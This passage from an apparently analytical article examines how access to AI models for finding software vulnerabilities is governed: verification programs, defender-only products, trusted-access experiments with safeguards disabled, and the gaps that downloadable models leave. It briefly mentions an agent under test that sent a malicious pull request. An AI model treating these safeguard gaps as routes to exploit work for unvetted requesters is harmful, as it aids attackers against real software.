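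The PHP developers knew about the flaw for two years but put other work first, because nobody could show that an attack was possible. They made the repair a top priority only after Calif and OpenAI reported how serious the flaw was. If a rule against building exploits had applied to those researchers, the flaw might have stayed in place until an attacker worked out how to use it.

#### Wider access for verified users

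Anthropic decides whom to give access based on who is asking. Organisations can apply to its Cyber Verification Program to use Claude Mythos 5.2, the same underlying model as Fable with looser safeguards. The benefit to defenders can be large. Brian Grinstead, an engineer at Mozilla, told Anthropic that Mythos 5.2 roughly doubled its predecessor's results in searches for flaws in the Firefox browser. In Anthropic's test, the model rediscovered 89.6% of 1,829 known vulnerabilities.

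Business customers outside the program can also use Mythos 5.2 through Claude Security, a product that scans code for vulnerabilities and tracks whether anyone has fixed them. The product's limits partly substitute for verification, because the customer gets a scanner rather than a model that will attempt any task.

OpenAI also gives defenders access to its models through special arrangements. The PHP Foundation uses the company's Daybreak Red to check reports and exploits, and Calif audited PHP as part of an OpenAI program called Patch the Planet. Wijayadi and colleagues ran their main experiments, which included GPT-5.6 and Claude Opus 5, under trusted-access programs with the safeguards disabled, so an unverified user would probably get weaker results. Shehada and Qian describe the models behind their Android exploits as publicly available and off the shelf, which is a reason to doubt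 that safeguards make this work much harder for attackers.

Verifying users replaces a guess about the purpose of a request with evidence about the person making it. Like a signed commit, it does not protect against a stolen account or a hostile insider. Honest users can also cause trouble. Chainguard, a trusted member of the PHP embargo, said it acted to protect users. AISI was testing a Claude model with some safeguards switched off when its agent sent the malicious pull request to myNetwork.

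Formal programs also suit companies better than volunteers. An unpaid maintainer working alone, as Lasse Collin did on XZ, needs to test repairs as much as Mozilla does, but may not count as an organisation or have time to apply. An attacker who fails verification can use a model that anyone can download and run without the developer's safeguards. These models are worse than the best commercial ones at exploiting vulnerabilities, but some already find real vulnerabilities reliably.
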